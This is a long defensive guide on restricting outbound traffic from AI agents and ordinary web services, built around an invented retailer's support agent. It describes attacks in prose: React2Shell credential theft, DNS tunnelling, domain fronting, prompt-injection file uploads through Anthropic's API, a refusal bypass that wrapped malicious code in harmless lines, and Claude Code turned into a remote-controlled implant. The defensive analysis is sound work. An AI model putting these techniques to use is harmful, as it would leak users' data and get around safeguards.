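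DataDome's *The AI Traffic Report* (2026) counts nearly 8 billion requests from AI agents since the start of the year, all to websites on the vendor's network, but this total doesn't show how many services a typical agent contacts.

Even an exact replication of the DockerGym study would be of limited use here. A workload that relies on a hosted model makes outbound calls by definition, so a yes-or-no measure of whether workloads make such calls would come out near 100%. Asking who controls the calls and what data they can carry is more useful.

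### The two kinds of workload side by side

Suppose the retailer's website also has an order-status page, where a customer types in an order number and sees where the parcel is. The service behind the page reads two private sources, the order database and the customer account database. It calls three outside services: the carrier's tracking API, email delivery and telemetry.

| | Order-status service | Support agent |
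|---|---|---|
| Who chooses the destination | The developer, in the code | The model, from tools the developer provides |
| Who chooses the content | The developer, as fixed fields | Mostly the model |
| Can input redirect it? | Only through a bug | Yes, in normal operation |
| Form of outgoing text | Tracking numbers and a template email | Search phrases, letters and whole conversations |
| Credentials in the container | 5 | 9 |
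| Pattern of traffic | The same few calls each time | The same hosts, but different calls for each question |

A destination that a developer fixed in advance can still become dangerous. Tsoukaladelis and colleagues found 82 images that looked up domains anyone could register. They bought several of these domains and monitored four, which three of the images contact. Over two months, 311 machines outside the laboratory connected to the team's server. An attacker could have bought the same domains and collected whatever those machines sent, though such an attack depends on a developer's mistake and some luck. An agent's destinations can change from one minute to the next, depending on the tool the model picks. In the runs that Li and colleagues recorded with Claude Code, a web search mostly produced traffic to the model provider, which carried out the search. Opening a page added a DNS lookup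 and a download from the site the model had chosen.

Input can redirect ordinary services too. In *SQL injection*, an attacker types a database command into a web form, and a badly written program passes it to the database, which runs it. Developers prevent this with parameterised queries, which keep the typed text separate from the command so that the database can never run it. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* (December 2025), David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that prompt injection has no such fix, because a model only predicts the next token from all the text so far and has no inherent boundary between instructions and data. Training and labelling can make the model better at telling them apart, but they don't create a boundary. The test results in the previous section are consistent with this, since newer models fail much less often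 but still fail.

The format of outgoing text determines how much data an attacker can hide in it. A 12-digit tracking number can carry about 40 bits (12 × log₂10), or less if the service sends only numbers that already exist in the order database. A program can check such a field exactly. The agent's emails have no fixed format, and one email can hold a customer's entire record in plain English. A filter has to determine whether that record belongs in the message, which depends on who will receive it.

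The gap in credentials is smaller, and counting them can mislead, because one key that can read every customer's record is worth more to a thief than five keys with narrow permissions. The agent tends to need broad permissions because nobody knows which customer will write next. The order-status service also needs broad access to its databases, but its code, rather than a model, decides which row to read.

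Predictable traffic makes it easier for a defender to notice a theft, and agents' traffic is far from random. *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks* (2026) reports 97.7% accuracy at identifying a model from encrypted traffic alone, and up to 90.7% at identifying the task that a team of agents was working on. Recognising that a task is malicious is harder. Li and colleagues tested 13 methods on 189 harmless runs and 20 malicious ones. All 13 were right at least 90% of the time, but so is a method that labels everything harmless, and seven of the 13 caught fewer than half of the malicious runs. Those runs were hacking tasks rather than thefts by prompt injection. The team also hid the destination addresses from the methods, so a company watching its own network would have more information to use. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) notes that this kind of analysis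 needs separately trained models for each agent and provider, and that the result is only a probability.

### Counting the routes

A simple way to compare the two workloads is to count the pairs of a private source and an outside destination. The agent has four sources and eight destinations, which make 32 pairs. The order-status service has two sources and three destinations, which make 6. By this count, the agent's exposure also grows faster, because each new outside service adds four pairs to the agent and two to the order-status service.

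This count gives every possible route equal weight, so a web search that reveals a town counts as much as a 9,000-token prompt. In four of the agent's 32 pairs, the destination has already received the data, because outside companies host or index three of the four sources. The count also includes routes that the software may not be able to move data along. The order-status service uses only three of its six routes. Its code sends order details to the carrier and by email, account details only by email, and neither to telemetry. In the agent, data from all four sources ends up in one context, and the model can copy any of it into a search phrase or an email.

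The count also leaves out the places where hostile text can enter. The agent reads untrusted text from at least four places (email, old tickets, delivery notes and search results), so counting entry points, sources and destinations together would give 4 × 4 × 8 = 128 combinations. Among MCP tool servers, *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025) found 121 that take in outside content, 149 that reach private data and 89 that can send data over the network. Only two servers do all three, but there are 121 × 149 × 89, or about 1.6 million, ways to choose one server for each role. Inspecting each server separately would pass nearly all of these combinations. Many users couldn't have assembled such a set when *A Measurement Study of Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (2025) examined 341 client programs, because 80.9% of them could connect to only one server. The other 65 allowed several at once.

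The biggest omission from both figures is the possibility that an attacker runs their own code in the container, which can happen to either workload. The list of destinations then grows to include every address the network allows.

### React2Shell

In December 2025, a flaw in React, a widely used toolkit for building websites, exposed many ordinary web services to attack. The flaw, which became known as *React2Shell*, was in how the part of React that runs on the server decodes incoming requests. Anyone could send a specially written request and run their own code on the server without logging in. The flaw received 10.0 on the standard severity scale, the highest possible score. React (2025) disclosed it on 3 December and released a fix the same day, but several organised groups began trying to exploit it within hours, according to *Prevent data exfiltration*, a guide from Amazon Web Services.

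JPCERT/CC, which coordinates responses to computer attacks in Japan, describes the attacks on one server in *Multiple Threat Actors Rapidly Exploit React2Shell* (2026). The first attempts to install cryptocurrency miners came two days after the disclosure. Over the next two days, attackers installed backdoors and more miners, and defaced the website. The operator found out on the evening of 7 December, when a user reported a problem.

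Other attackers used the flaw to steal credentials in bulk. Cisco Talos' *UAT-10608* describes an automated campaign that compromised at least 766 servers, within 24 hours. Cisco's threat researchers found the thieves' own control panel open to the internet and counted what was in it:

| Stolen credential | Share of the 766 servers |
|---|---|
| Database credentials | 91.5% |
| SSH private keys, which open other machines | 78.2% |
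| AWS credentials | 25.6% |
| Live keys for Stripe, a payment company | 11.4% |
| GitHub tokens | 8.6% |

On average, the thieves took at least two of these five kinds from each server on the list. The sample contains only servers they had already broken into, so it doesn't represent web servers in general, but it shows that an ordinary service can hold more than one kind of valuable credential. The stolen credentials also included keys for OpenAI and Anthropic, which any program that calls a hosted model might hold.

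A single React2Shell attack was worse than a typical prompt injection. An injected instruction can only use the tools that the agent already has, while React2Shell attackers could read every file and setting that the web server's process could read. But companies could fix React2Shell by installing an update, and no update ends prompt injection. An agent is exposed to both kinds of problem, because the program around the model is ordinary software and has bugs too.

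### Whether agents need different controls

AWS concludes from React2Shell that agents' outbound traffic should pass through the same firewall and domain allowlists as any other workload's. The credential theft supports this advice. The thieves' first program had to fetch a longer script from elsewhere, and that script sent its results to their own server, usually on port 8080. The victims' websites had no reason to contact that server, so a strict allowlist would have blocked the connection, as one blocked the agent's requests to the attacker's domain in the eBay tests. Using one path for all traffic also leaves fewer exceptions that someone might forget. AWS sells such firewalls, but the advice applies to any vendor's.

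David C wants more than this for software built on language models. If a model that can call tools reads hostile text, the designer should assume the attacker can call those tools. David C therefore recommends limits that ordinary code enforces regardless of the model's output, and says that a language model may be a bad choice for a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk. One such limit, from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, is to reduce a model's privileges to those of the person whose text it is processing.

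At the retailer, this rule would work well at first. After the agent reads the customer's email about the cracked lid, it could see only her own record and orders, which she is allowed to see. Then it searches the web for carrier delays and reads a page by an unknown author, who has no right to see anything. Read strictly, the rule would now require the agent to give up her record and its ability to send email, so it couldn't finish the reply. The retailer would have to move the search into a separate step that returns only something harmless, such as a number of days. The rule is sound, but it requires more design work and makes the agent less flexible.

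AWS and David C disagree less than it first appears. AWS acknowledges that agents' need for outside tools makes allowlists harder to design, and it recommends adding filters for prompt attacks. A firewall is also the kind of limit David C asks for. They still disagree about whether the shared path is enough. It isn't enough for the retailer's agent, because a search phrase containing a customer's address would go to a company on the allowlist. The order-status service needs a second layer much less, because its code puts only fixed fields into its requests.

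### Where the distinction breaks down

Some programs that use a language model need few extra controls. The retailer might have a nightly job that sends each new ticket to a model in a single call, asks for one of ten category labels, and files the ticket under that label. The job gives the model no tools and rejects any answer that isn't on the list. A hostile ticket could cause the model to pick the wrong label, but it couldn't change where the job sends data or add text to a request. The model provider would still receive every ticket, as would any outside company the retailer hired to sort them.

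Many real agents may be closer to this job than to the free-ranging agents in research papers. In *Measuring Agents in Production*, Pan, Arabzadeh and colleagues (2025) surveyed the developers of 86 agents in production or pilot use and found that 68% run at most ten steps before a person intervenes. They conclude that developers deliberately give up capability to keep control. The share may have fallen since the survey closed in October 2025, because models have improved. Short runs are not necessarily safe, either. The retailer's agent answers the question about the cracked lid with three model calls, and the web-page attack in the previous section needs only three tool calls.

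Some ordinary software puts more at risk than any support agent does. An *integration hub* copies data between business applications according to fixed rules, such as adding every new order to the accounts. A hub that links 20 outside applications, each able to send data to any other, holds 20 credentials and has 20 × 19 = 380 pairs of source and destination. Its rules determine which pairs it uses, so hostile text in an order can't open a new route. But someone who breaks into the hub gets all 20 credentials at once. Cisco Talos found n8n, a program for automating workflows, running on some of the compromised servers and lists it among the high-value targets for further attacks. A hub like this may need protection more urgently than the agent, if the retailer runs one.

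## Limiting where the workload can connect

Any workload, with or without a language model, leaks less if it can reach only the systems it needs. *Default-deny egress* is a policy of refusing every outbound connection that no rule permits. A short allowlist of this kind blocked every theft in the eBay tests. For the retailer's support agent, the work goes in this order:

1. Record the outbound connections for a while without blocking any.
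2. Find a reason for each destination, and drop those that have none.
3. Refuse everything else.
4. Enforce the refusal outside the agent container, where the agent can't change it.

### Recording and justifying connections

Developers know which services they wrote into an agent, but not always which ones its libraries contact. A firewall can record both. AWS's *From log analysis to rule creation* describes a mode of Network Firewall, a cloud firewall, that records the domains a network contacts over the web for up to 30 days. The resulting report lists each domain with the number of attempts to reach it, the number of machines that made them, and the times of the first and last attempts. An operator can then copy the list of domains into a firewall rule.

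It is safer to review the list by hand first. If an attacker is already using the agent to steal data, the attacker's server will be on the list. The report also leaves out database connections, DNS lookups and anything else that doesn't use web protocols, and it can't show a destination that the workload needs only in an emergency. For each entry, someone should write down which feature needs it and what data it receives. This will usually show that no feature needs the telemetry sent by a forgotten library.

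A log-only period blocks nothing, so an attack during it can still get data out. The retailer can avoid most of this risk by logging the connections of a test copy of the agent, loaded with invented customer records, while asking it questions that use every tool. A few days should be enough, since the agent's tools connect to fixed hosts.

AWS recommends starting with a broad allowlist, even one that includes whole domain endings such as `.gov`, so that a company reaches default deny quickly and can narrow the rules later. Anthropic's guide to sandboxing its coding agent instead recommends starting with minimal permissions and adding to them. The broad approach suits a company with hundreds of undocumented services. The retailer's agent has eight outside destinations, all of which its developers chose, so its allowlist can start with exact domain names. If the list does end up with a broad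 rule, the team can use the alert setting that AWS (2025) added to its domain lists to log matching traffic without interrupting it, and see what the rule allows before tightening it.

### The retailer's allowlist

The hostnames and addresses below are invented, except for the two package registries.

| Destination | Purpose | Open |
|---|---|---|
| `api.model.example`, port 443 | Model API | Run time |
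| `api.embed.example`, port 443 | Embedding API | Run time |
| `retailer.vectors.example`, port 443 | Vector database | Run time |
| `api.search.example`, port 443 | Web search | Run time |
| `retailer.crm.example`, port 443 | Customer records | Run time |
| `retailer.tickets.example`, port 443 | Ticketing | Run time |
| `api.mail.example`, port 443 | Email delivery | Run time |
| `ingest.telemetry.example`, port 443 | Telemetry | Run time |
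| `10.0.20.15`, port 5432 | Order database, on the retailer's own network | Run time |
| `pypi.org` and `files.pythonhosted.org`, port 443 | Python packages | Build time only, from the build machine |

Every allowlist entry is an exact name because wildcards often cover more than they seem to. AWS's *Control which domains your AI agents can access* includes `.amazonaws.com` in its sample allowlist, then warns that this entry also permits public storage buckets and function addresses hosted on AWS. An attacker can open an AWS account and create either in minutes. The same guide notes that pages on an approved site may not load fully until the operator also permits the content-delivery domains behind them, such as `cloudfront.net`, but anyone can rent space there too. Docker gives a similar warning about `github.com`, where users publish their own content.

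Only a build machine can reach the package registries, and only while it assembles the container image. That machine holds no customer data, and the finished container doesn't need to contact a registry because its packages are already installed. Some software tries to download packages when it starts, as many of the public images in the DockerGym study seem to have done, and the retailer would have to move those downloads into the build. Registry connections are worth restricting this way even when they go through a proxy. According to OpenAI, a package-registry proxy was the weak point in its July 2026 incident, in which agents got out of a test environment.

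### What each layer can see

The retailer can apply the allowlist at several points between the container and the internet. These controls differ in how much of a request they can read, mostly because of *TLS* (Transport Layer Security), the encryption behind every web address that starts with https. Suppose the agent container contacts the email service directly:

1. The program asks DNS for the numerical address of `api.mail.example`.
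2. It opens a connection to that address on port 443.
3. It sends a greeting that includes the hostname in plain text, because one machine may serve many sites. This field is the *server name indication* (SNI).
4. The server presents a certificate, a signed document that proves it controls the hostname, and the two sides agree on encryption keys.
5. The program sends the actual request, now encrypted.

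| Control | What it can read of the email request |
|---|---|
| Kubernetes NetworkPolicy | The numerical address and the port |
| Name-aware policy | The address and port, plus the hostname from the DNS answer |
| DNS filter | The hostname in the lookup, but nothing of the connection |
| Server-name firewall | The address, the port and the hostname in the greeting |
| Egress proxy | The hostname and port that the program asks for |
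| Egress proxy with TLS termination | Everything, including the recipient and the text of the email |

*TLS termination* means decrypting traffic at a proxy so that the proxy can inspect it, then encrypting it again for the destination.

### Kubernetes network policies

Kubernetes runs containers in *pods*, groups of one or more containers that share a network address. According to Kubernetes' *Network Policies*, a pod can open any outbound connection until some policy selects it for egress. After that, it can open only the connections that a policy lists. If the retailer's proxy and order database run on their own machines outside the cluster, the agent's policy needs just two entries:

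```yaml
apiVersion: networking.k8s.io/v1
kind: NetworkPolicy
metadata:
  name: support-agent-egress
spec:
  podSelector:
    matchLabels:
      app: support-agent
  policyTypes:
    - Egress
  egress:
    - to:
        - ipBlock:
            cidr: 10.0.10.5/32    # egress proxy
      ports:
        - protocol: TCP
          port: 8080
    - to:
        - ipBlock:
            cidr: 10.0.20.15/32   # order database
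      ports:
        - protocol: TCP
          port: 5432
```

The network policy doesn't list the outside services because the container reaches them only through the proxy. Most teams have to add a rule allowing DNS, since a default-deny policy blocks it, but this policy omits that rule because the container can leave name lookups to the proxy.

Such a policy can fail without warning. Kubernetes relies on a network plugin to enforce it, and if the plugin doesn't support policies, Kubernetes stores the policy but it has no effect. A pod that uses its host machine's network directly is usually exempt, since most plugins can't tell its traffic from the machine's own. Every pod can also reach the machine it runs on regardless of the policy, so the agent can connect to any service listening there. Policies can only add permissions, so if another team writes a broad policy that also selects the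 agent's pod, the pod gains every connection that policy allows.

NetworkPolicy can't log the connections it accepts or refuses, so Kubernetes itself keeps no record of these mistakes. Operators can find them by trying a connection that the policy should refuse and seeing whether it succeeds.

The metadata service, which supplies temporary credentials, should have its own rule because requests to it bypass the central firewall and its domain allowlist. On most large clouds, the service's address is 169.254.169.254. AWS's *Enhance Amazon EKS network security posture with DNS and admin network policies* gives a rule for EKS, Amazon's managed Kubernetes service, that blocks every pod in the cluster from reaching this address. Unlike an ordinary NetworkPolicy, the rule takes precedence over anything an individual team writes. If the address is still open, a web request to it from inside the container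 gets a response instead of timing out.

### Policies that use names

Outside services change their IP addresses often, which makes a list of addresses hard to maintain. Some Kubernetes plugins therefore accept hostnames. Cilium's *Layer 3 Policies* describes how Cilium, a popular open-source plugin, intercepts the DNS answers that pods receive, notes which addresses belong to the permitted names, and allows connections to those addresses. Google Cloud's *Control Pod egress traffic using FQDN network policies* covers an equivalent for Google's managed Kubernetes. Amazon's version works only on machines that run in Auto Mode, according to AWS's *Amazon EKS introduces enhanced network security policies* (2025).

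By the time a connection opens, the domain name has been resolved to an IP address, and Cilium's documentation says that these rules share all the limitations of address rules. A large hosting network may serve thousands of sites from one address. If the email service and an attacker's site share an address, a rule that permits connections to the email service also permits connections to the attacker's site. Cilium's records would show only a permitted address, so another control would have to read the SNI to detect the attacker's site.

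### DNS filtering

A network cut off from the internet can still make DNS lookups. AWS warns that its built-in resolver looks up public names even for a private network with no internet gateway and no route out. These lookups also bypass Network Firewall, so an agent with a command line could use them to leak data. The fix is a filter at the resolver, which AWS sells as DNS Firewall.

Such a filter can look for signs of *DNS tunnelling*, which hides data in lookups. AWS describes a detector that compares each name with the patterns of ordinary domains, because encoded data tends to look like random characters. In the logs, tunnelling appears as a series of long, unique names under one domain. A large theft should therefore stand out, but the theft of an access key may not, because a key fits in a single lookup.

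An allowlist avoids this problem because it doesn't depend on what the names look like. The resolver never forwards a lookup for an unlisted domain, so the attacker's name server never receives the data.

Barking Iguana's *How to Allowlist Egress by Hostname* describes two ways a program can bypass a DNS filter. The program can connect directly to an IP address it already has, or send its lookups to another resolver inside encrypted web traffic. A defender can spot both by searching for connections to addresses that the approved resolver never returned.

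### Firewalls that read the server name

A server-name firewall must let a connection open before it can read the greeting. It then compares the SNI with its allowlist and drops the connection if the name isn't there. AWS's guide to domain control therefore warns against a stricter default setting, which would block the approved sites too. The brief opening lets an attacker's server detect the connection attempt. AWS's session holding option keeps traffic from reaching the destination until the firewall has checked the name.

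The program that opens the connection can put any server name in the greeting. An attacker who runs code in the container can connect to their own server while giving `api.model.example` as the name. AWS's *Stateful domain list rule groups in Amazon Network Firewall* says that the firewall evaluates domain lists by the name, not the IP address. In the logs, the theft would look like another call to the model API, except for an unfamiliar IP address.

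AWS now has a setting that blocks this by permitting a connection only if the SNI is on the allowlist and DNS returned the destination address for that name. The setting uses DNS lookups from networks that have DNS Firewall, as AWS's *Using DNS Firewall to filter outbound DNS traffic* explains, so the retailer would need both products.

Even this doesn't stop *domain fronting*, which works when the attacker's site and a permitted site share a content-delivery network. The program connects to the permitted site's address and gives that site's name in the greeting, but asks for the attacker's site inside the encrypted request. The shared network then delivers the request to the attacker. Only TLS termination can reveal the mismatch. Newer browsers and libraries can also encrypt the SNI itself, using a feature called Encrypted Client Hello, and AWS suggests decrypting the traffic in this case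 too.

The retailer's agent can't falsify a server name with its own tools, because they use standard web libraries that fill in the name correctly. To use these tricks, an attacker would have to run code in the container, which they could do through a flaw like React2Shell or an agent with a command line.

### An egress proxy as the only way out

An egress proxy makes all of the container's connections to outside services. The container sends it a hostname, and the proxy checks the name, looks up the address itself and opens the connection. An attacker gains nothing by falsifying the server name, because the proxy chooses the address. Domain fronting still works unless the proxy also terminates TLS.

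The usual way to direct programs to a proxy is to set the variables `HTTP_PROXY` and `HTTPS_PROXY` in the container. Most programs read these variables, but they don't have to. Anthropic notes that `fetch()`, the standard function for web requests in Node.js, ignores them by default. (In version 24 and later, setting `NODE_USE_ENV_PROXY=1` changes this.) If the network permits direct connections, a program that ignores the variables works normally and bypasses all of the proxy's rules. Its destinations then appear in the network's connection logs but not in the proxy's. Blocking direct connections prevents this bypass, at the inconvenience of making such programs fail.

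Workloads can bypass AWS's own proxy, still in public preview in mid-2026, if an operator installs it without other controls. AWS's *Pre-requisites* says that workloads need to be configured to use the proxy, and InfoQ (2025) quotes a warning from the proxy's developers that its rules don't apply to traffic merely routed to the NAT gateway, the network's shared exit to the internet. The operator has to close that exit to everything except the proxy.

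*How to force AI agents to use an egress proxy* describes how the developer simedw's team at the AI company V7 reached a working design. Setting proxy environment variables was not enough, because a few lines of Python could open a connection without them. The team then tried one of Docker's internal networks, which has no route to the outside. However, Docker still attached a DNS resolver to it, and containers could reach services on the host machine and any other port on the proxy. Rules for IPv4 addresses also had no effect on IPv6 traffic.

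V7's final version puts firewall rules on the host. They allow traffic only to the proxy's address and port and drop everything else, including DNS. A separate rule protects the host, and IPv6 is off. The team kept the proxy variables only so that programs that use them can find the proxy.

The proxy should compare a hostname with the allowlist before looking it up in DNS, since the lookup alone could carry data to an attacker's name server. AWS's *How does Network Firewall Proxy work?* describes a rule phase that runs before DNS for this purpose. After the lookup, V7's proxy rejects any name that resolves to a private or internal address, such as the metadata service's. It then connects to the exact address it checked, so an attacker can't redirect the connection by changing the DNS answer after the check.

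Anthropic describes an even stricter arrangement in which Docker's `--network none` option gives the container no outside network, so direct connections and DNS lookups both fail. The operator shares one *Unix socket* (a special file through which programs on the same machine exchange data) with the container, and the proxy listens at the other end. The operator must be careful about which sockets to share, because Docker's own control socket would give the agent power over the whole host, as Anthropic's sandboxing guide points out. The retailer could use this arrangement if the order database also sat behind a proxy, because a container without a network can't reach it directly.

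All of this can be done with common software. An engineer writing on the blog of the CNCF, the foundation that hosts Kubernetes, describes building a similar boundary on a single machine with NGINX, a common web server. Firewall rules dropped all outbound traffic that didn't go through NGINX. NGINX recorded every request and, in one configuration, permitted only two domains. GitHub Next's *Agentic Workflow Firewall* offers a ready-made domain allowlist for coding agents.

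### The AWS design as a worked example

A larger company needs the same controls across many workloads, and AWS's guide to preventing data exfiltration describes a design for this. Each application runs in its own *virtual private cloud* (VPC), a private network inside the cloud. A central router called Transit Gateway connects the VPCs and sends all internet-bound traffic to one Network Firewall.

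If the retailer used this design, a call from its agent to the model API would go as follows:

1. The egress proxy in the agent's VPC accepts the request and looks up `api.model.example`.
2. DNS Firewall, at that VPC's resolver, checks the name and permits the lookup.
3. The proxy opens a connection, and Transit Gateway passes it to Network Firewall.
4. Network Firewall reads the SNI, finds it on the allowlist, and confirms that the address came from the lookup.
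5. The traffic leaves through a NAT gateway.

AWS's basic design sends the agent's traffic directly to the firewall. Adding the proxy lets the retailer give each workload its own list and keep the central rules simple. Calls to AWS's own services take a private route instead of the internet, and a policy on that route can limit which companies' storage they reach.

By default, Network Firewall's domain lists apply only to traffic that starts in the firewall's own VPC. In this central layout, every workload is in another VPC, so AWS's documentation tells operators to add those networks to the `HOME_NET` setting. If the retailer forgot, the agent's traffic could go unfiltered even though the console showed a correct allowlist. DNS Firewall has a similar gap, because each VPC needs its own association with the filter, and a new VPC may not have one. In either case, a request to a domain that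 isn't on the list would succeed. Firewall rule changes also take a few minutes to spread, so a test right after an edit can give the wrong result.

AWS recommends turning on DNS Firewall first and building the central firewall in a second phase. That order makes sense for a company that already has many workloads, since the DNS filter needs no changes to routing. The retailer has only one agent to protect, so it could skip the central firewall at first. Anthropic's steps for cloud deployments require only a proxy, a private network with no internet gateway, and a cloud firewall rule that allows traffic only to the proxy. DNS Firewall would still be worth adding, because the resolver can send DNS queries out of the network even without an internet gateway.

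### Agents that need the open web

An allowlist could defeat the purpose of an agent that looks things up. The web-research agents that Jeong and colleagues measured averaged at least 65 domains per question, and nobody could have listed those domains in advance.

Many agents need less of the web than this. The retailer's agent searches for delivery delays, and the retailer uses perhaps a dozen carriers, each of which publishes notices on its own site. Cloud providers sell tools that can restrict browsing this way. AWS's *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore adds support for Chrome policies and custom root CA* (2026) describes a browser for agents that an administrator can limit to certain addresses, with downloads and the password manager turned off. AWS's *Web Search in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore adds domain and published date filtering* (2026) describes a search tool that accepts lists of up to 100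 domains.

The search tool accepts domain lists from both the agent and an administrator. The agent can supply a list with each search to help it get relevant results, but this gives no protection because an injected instruction could change the list. The administrator can set another list at the gateway, where the agent can't change it. Both lists filter only the results, so anything the model puts in the search phrase still goes out.

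If an agent needs access to the whole web, it is better to let it browse from a container that holds no credentials or sensitive data.

### Splitting the retailer's agent

The retailer can divide its agent into two containers. The agent container keeps the private data and loses web search. A second container, the browsing container, can open any public website but holds no customer data and has no access to the retailer's internal systems. A proxy still stands in front of it to block private addresses. The question about the cracked lid would then work like this:

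1. The agent container reads the customer's message, record and order as before.
2. The model asks for a delay check. It supplies no details.
3. Ordinary code takes the carrier and the delivery region from the order and sends two short codes to the browsing container.
4. A separate model in the browsing container searches the web, opens the carrier's notice and estimates the delay.
5. The browsing container returns a single value, which must be a whole number of days from 0 to 14 or the word "unknown".
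6. Code in the agent container rejects anything else and gives the value to the first model, which writes the reply.

A page with a hidden instruction can still take over the model in the browsing container, but that model has no customer record to send. It can't pass the instruction on either, because its reply has only 16 possible values, or four bits, which is far too little for a sentence.

It matters that code, not the model, fills in step 3. With 12 carriers and 120 regions, there are 1,440 possible requests, so each one can carry about 10.5 bits (log₂ 1,440). If the model chose the codes, an injected instruction in a customer's email could make it encode a ten-digit phone number in four requests. An attacker would still need to see what the browsing container searched for, but a malicious page in the results might make that possible.

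The structured reply also makes the split less useful. The original agent could tell the customer that a flood had closed the local depot and that she could collect her parcel from another one. The new agent can only say that parcels are running two days late. It can't open a link she sends or check whether a lid from another grinder would fit. The retailer could add fields for common cases, such as a reason chosen from a list of ten. A free-text summary would restore most of the lost detail, but an attacker could influence its wording. Anthropic's coding agent summarises search results before they enter the context. The company says this reduces the risk of prompt injection, but doesn't claim that it eliminates the risk.

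Some risk remains even with fixed fields. An attacker can put a false 14-day delay on a web page, and the agent will repeat it to the customer. An attacker who controls the browsing container can run up charges on its search and model accounts, or use it to send requests to other sites.

The agent container is safer than before but still exposed. It now connects to seven outside services instead of eight, which reduces the pairs of private source and outside destination from 32 to 28, and it no longer reads web pages. It still reads email from strangers in the same context as customers' records. An instruction hidden in one of those emails can't make the agent connect to a server outside the allowlist, but it could make the agent send the records through any of the seven services on it.

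## Limiting what can be sent to approved services

An allowlist controls which services a workload can contact, but most of those services can do far more than the workload needs. An email service will deliver to any address, and a storage service will save files to any customer's account. For each approved service, the retailer therefore has to allow only the operations, accounts and recipients that its agent uses. Anthropic learned this from a flaw in one of its products.

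### Files that left through Anthropic's own API

Claude Cowork is an Anthropic agent for office work. It runs code in a *virtual machine* (VM), a simulated computer with its own operating system. The VM can access only the folders the user selects. Willison (2026) explains in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* that the VM could contact only a short list of domains, to protect users against data theft by prompt injection. The list included `api.anthropic.com`, because Cowork can't work without calling the model.

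Two days after Anthropic released a preview of Cowork in January 2026, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated this attack:

1. A user connects a folder of confidential property files, then uploads a Word document found online that claims to help analyse such files.
2. The document contains an instruction in white, 1-point text, along with the attacker's own Anthropic API key.
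3. Claude follows the instruction and runs a command that uploads the largest file it can find to Anthropic's Files API, using the attacker's key.
4. The proxy sees an approved domain and lets the request through.
5. The file appears in the attacker's Anthropic account, where the attacker can ask Claude questions about it.

The attack on Cowork required no approval from the user. PromptArmor ran the demonstration on Claude Haiku, Anthropic's small model, but a similar attack made the stronger Opus 4.5 upload customer records.

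*Claude Pirate*, an October 2025 post on the security blog Embrace The Red, had already described the same upload from the Claude chat product, which also runs code. Claude often refused when the hidden instruction contained a readable API key. Encoding the key didn't reliably prevent refusals, but surrounding the malicious code with harmless lines that printed "Hello, world" did. Anthropic closed the vulnerability report within an hour as out of scope, and five days later said this had been a mistake.

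Anthropic eventually fixed Cowork with a second proxy, inside the VM, that decrypts requests to its API. Anthropic says this proxy passes only requests carrying the token the VM received for its own session, so it rejects an attacker's key. It also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something themselves. The check has to happen on the user's side because the attacker's key is valid, and on Anthropic's servers the theft looks like a customer uploading their own file.

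Anthropic concludes that adding a domain to an allowlist permits every function reachable there. By permitting one domain, it had also permitted uploads to any Anthropic account. The same applies to other companies' services, such as GitHub, which a coding agent's allowlist will often include. Security Point Break (2026) describes a malicious JavaScript package that tried to upload files from the folder where Claude keeps users' documents to an attacker-controlled GitHub account.

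### A stolen key for the right account

Checking whose key a request carries doesn't help if the attacker has stolen an approved key. *Living off the AI* (November 2026), by Darktrace, which sells network security products, demonstrates how an attacker could control Claude Code through *memory stores*, text files that Anthropic keeps so that agents can remember things between sessions. The test assumes that the attacker has already broken into a developer's machine and found the user's Claude credentials.

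*Stolen Claude API keys can turn Claude Code into a remote-controlled implant* (Zorz, 2026) describes an attack on a simulated company network. A small program kept launching Claude Code with its confirmation prompts turned off. Each new process logged its start in one memory file, read a job from a second, and wrote the results to a third. The operator sent nine jobs in plain English. Claude found a password on an open file share, generated 190 possible usernames, and tried the password with them until one worked. It then used that account to fetch a 1 GB file and sent the file to the Files API in three parts.

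The operator's instructions and the stolen data all travelled through `api.anthropic.com`, where a coding agent's traffic normally goes. Darktrace did not exploit a flaw in Anthropic's platform and has not seen the technique in real attacks. Its AI chief, Tim Bazalgette, told Zorz that exposure depends mainly on whether a provider's API stores text as well as running a model. OpenAI has an equivalent file service, though Darktrace tested only Anthropic's.

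A rule that accepts any key from the company's own account would have allowed these uploads. Cowork's stricter rule, which accepts only one session's token, would have refused any other key, but it would not have stopped a theft that used the session token itself. A rule that allows model calls but blocks file uploads would have stopped these uploads regardless of the key used.

### TLS termination

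These rules all require TLS termination because the key, the operation and the content are inside the encrypted request. The egress proxy presents the container with its own certificate for `api.model.example` and opens a second encrypted connection to the real service. The container accepts the proxy's certificate only if the operator has configured the container to trust the authority that signed it.

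The first drawback is that set-up. Python and Node.js programs often carry their own lists of trusted certificate authorities, so adding the proxy's authority to the operating system's list may not be enough. Some programs accept only one particular certificate from a service and won't connect through the proxy. The proxy also has to check the real service's certificate, since the container no longer can. If it doesn't, someone between the proxy and the service could read all the traffic between them.

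Decryption also adds a little delay, and a badly configured proxy may hold back a model's reply until it is complete instead of passing it on word by word. More seriously, the proxy can now read every prompt, customer record and credential that passes through it. A break-in at the proxy would be worse than one at most of the services behind it, so its logs shouldn't contain full requests by default.

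The retailer can avoid some of this work. Many client libraries let a developer change the address they call, so the agent can send its model requests unencrypted to the proxy, which forwards them over an encrypted connection. This setup doesn't require a substitute certificate, but the link between the container and the proxy must be private.

### Rules by method and path

Once the proxy can read a request, it can check the request's *method* and *path*. The method is the kind of action, such as GET, which normally reads data, or POST, which normally submits it. The path is the part of the address after the domain. A rule might permit `POST /v1/messages` on the model API and refuse `POST /v1/files`. AWS offers such rules in the preview of its proxy. NVIDIA's *What is the best way to prevent AI agents from exfiltrating data* (2026) describes OpenShell, a sandbox for agents that also limits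 which programs can reach each destination. Allowing only the agent's own program to call the model API would block calls from a command-line tool like the one in the Cowork attack. NVIDIA gives no test results for OpenShell.

NVIDIA suggests allowing GET requests and blocking POST requests that could carry data out. This helps against file uploads, but a GET request can still carry stolen text in its URL. Blocking POST would also stop the retailer's agent completely, because model calls, embeddings and vector searches all use POST. Rules about URL paths and request content are more useful here.

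The agent container has seven outside services left after the retailer moved web search into a separate container. It could limit them like this:

| Service | Permitted | Refused |
|---|---|---|
| Model API | New model calls | File uploads, memory stores |
| Embedding API | One short phrase per request | Bulk jobs |
| Vector database | Searches of the returns policy and product guides | Adding, changing or exporting passages |
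| Customer records | Reading the current customer's record | Other records, lists, exports |
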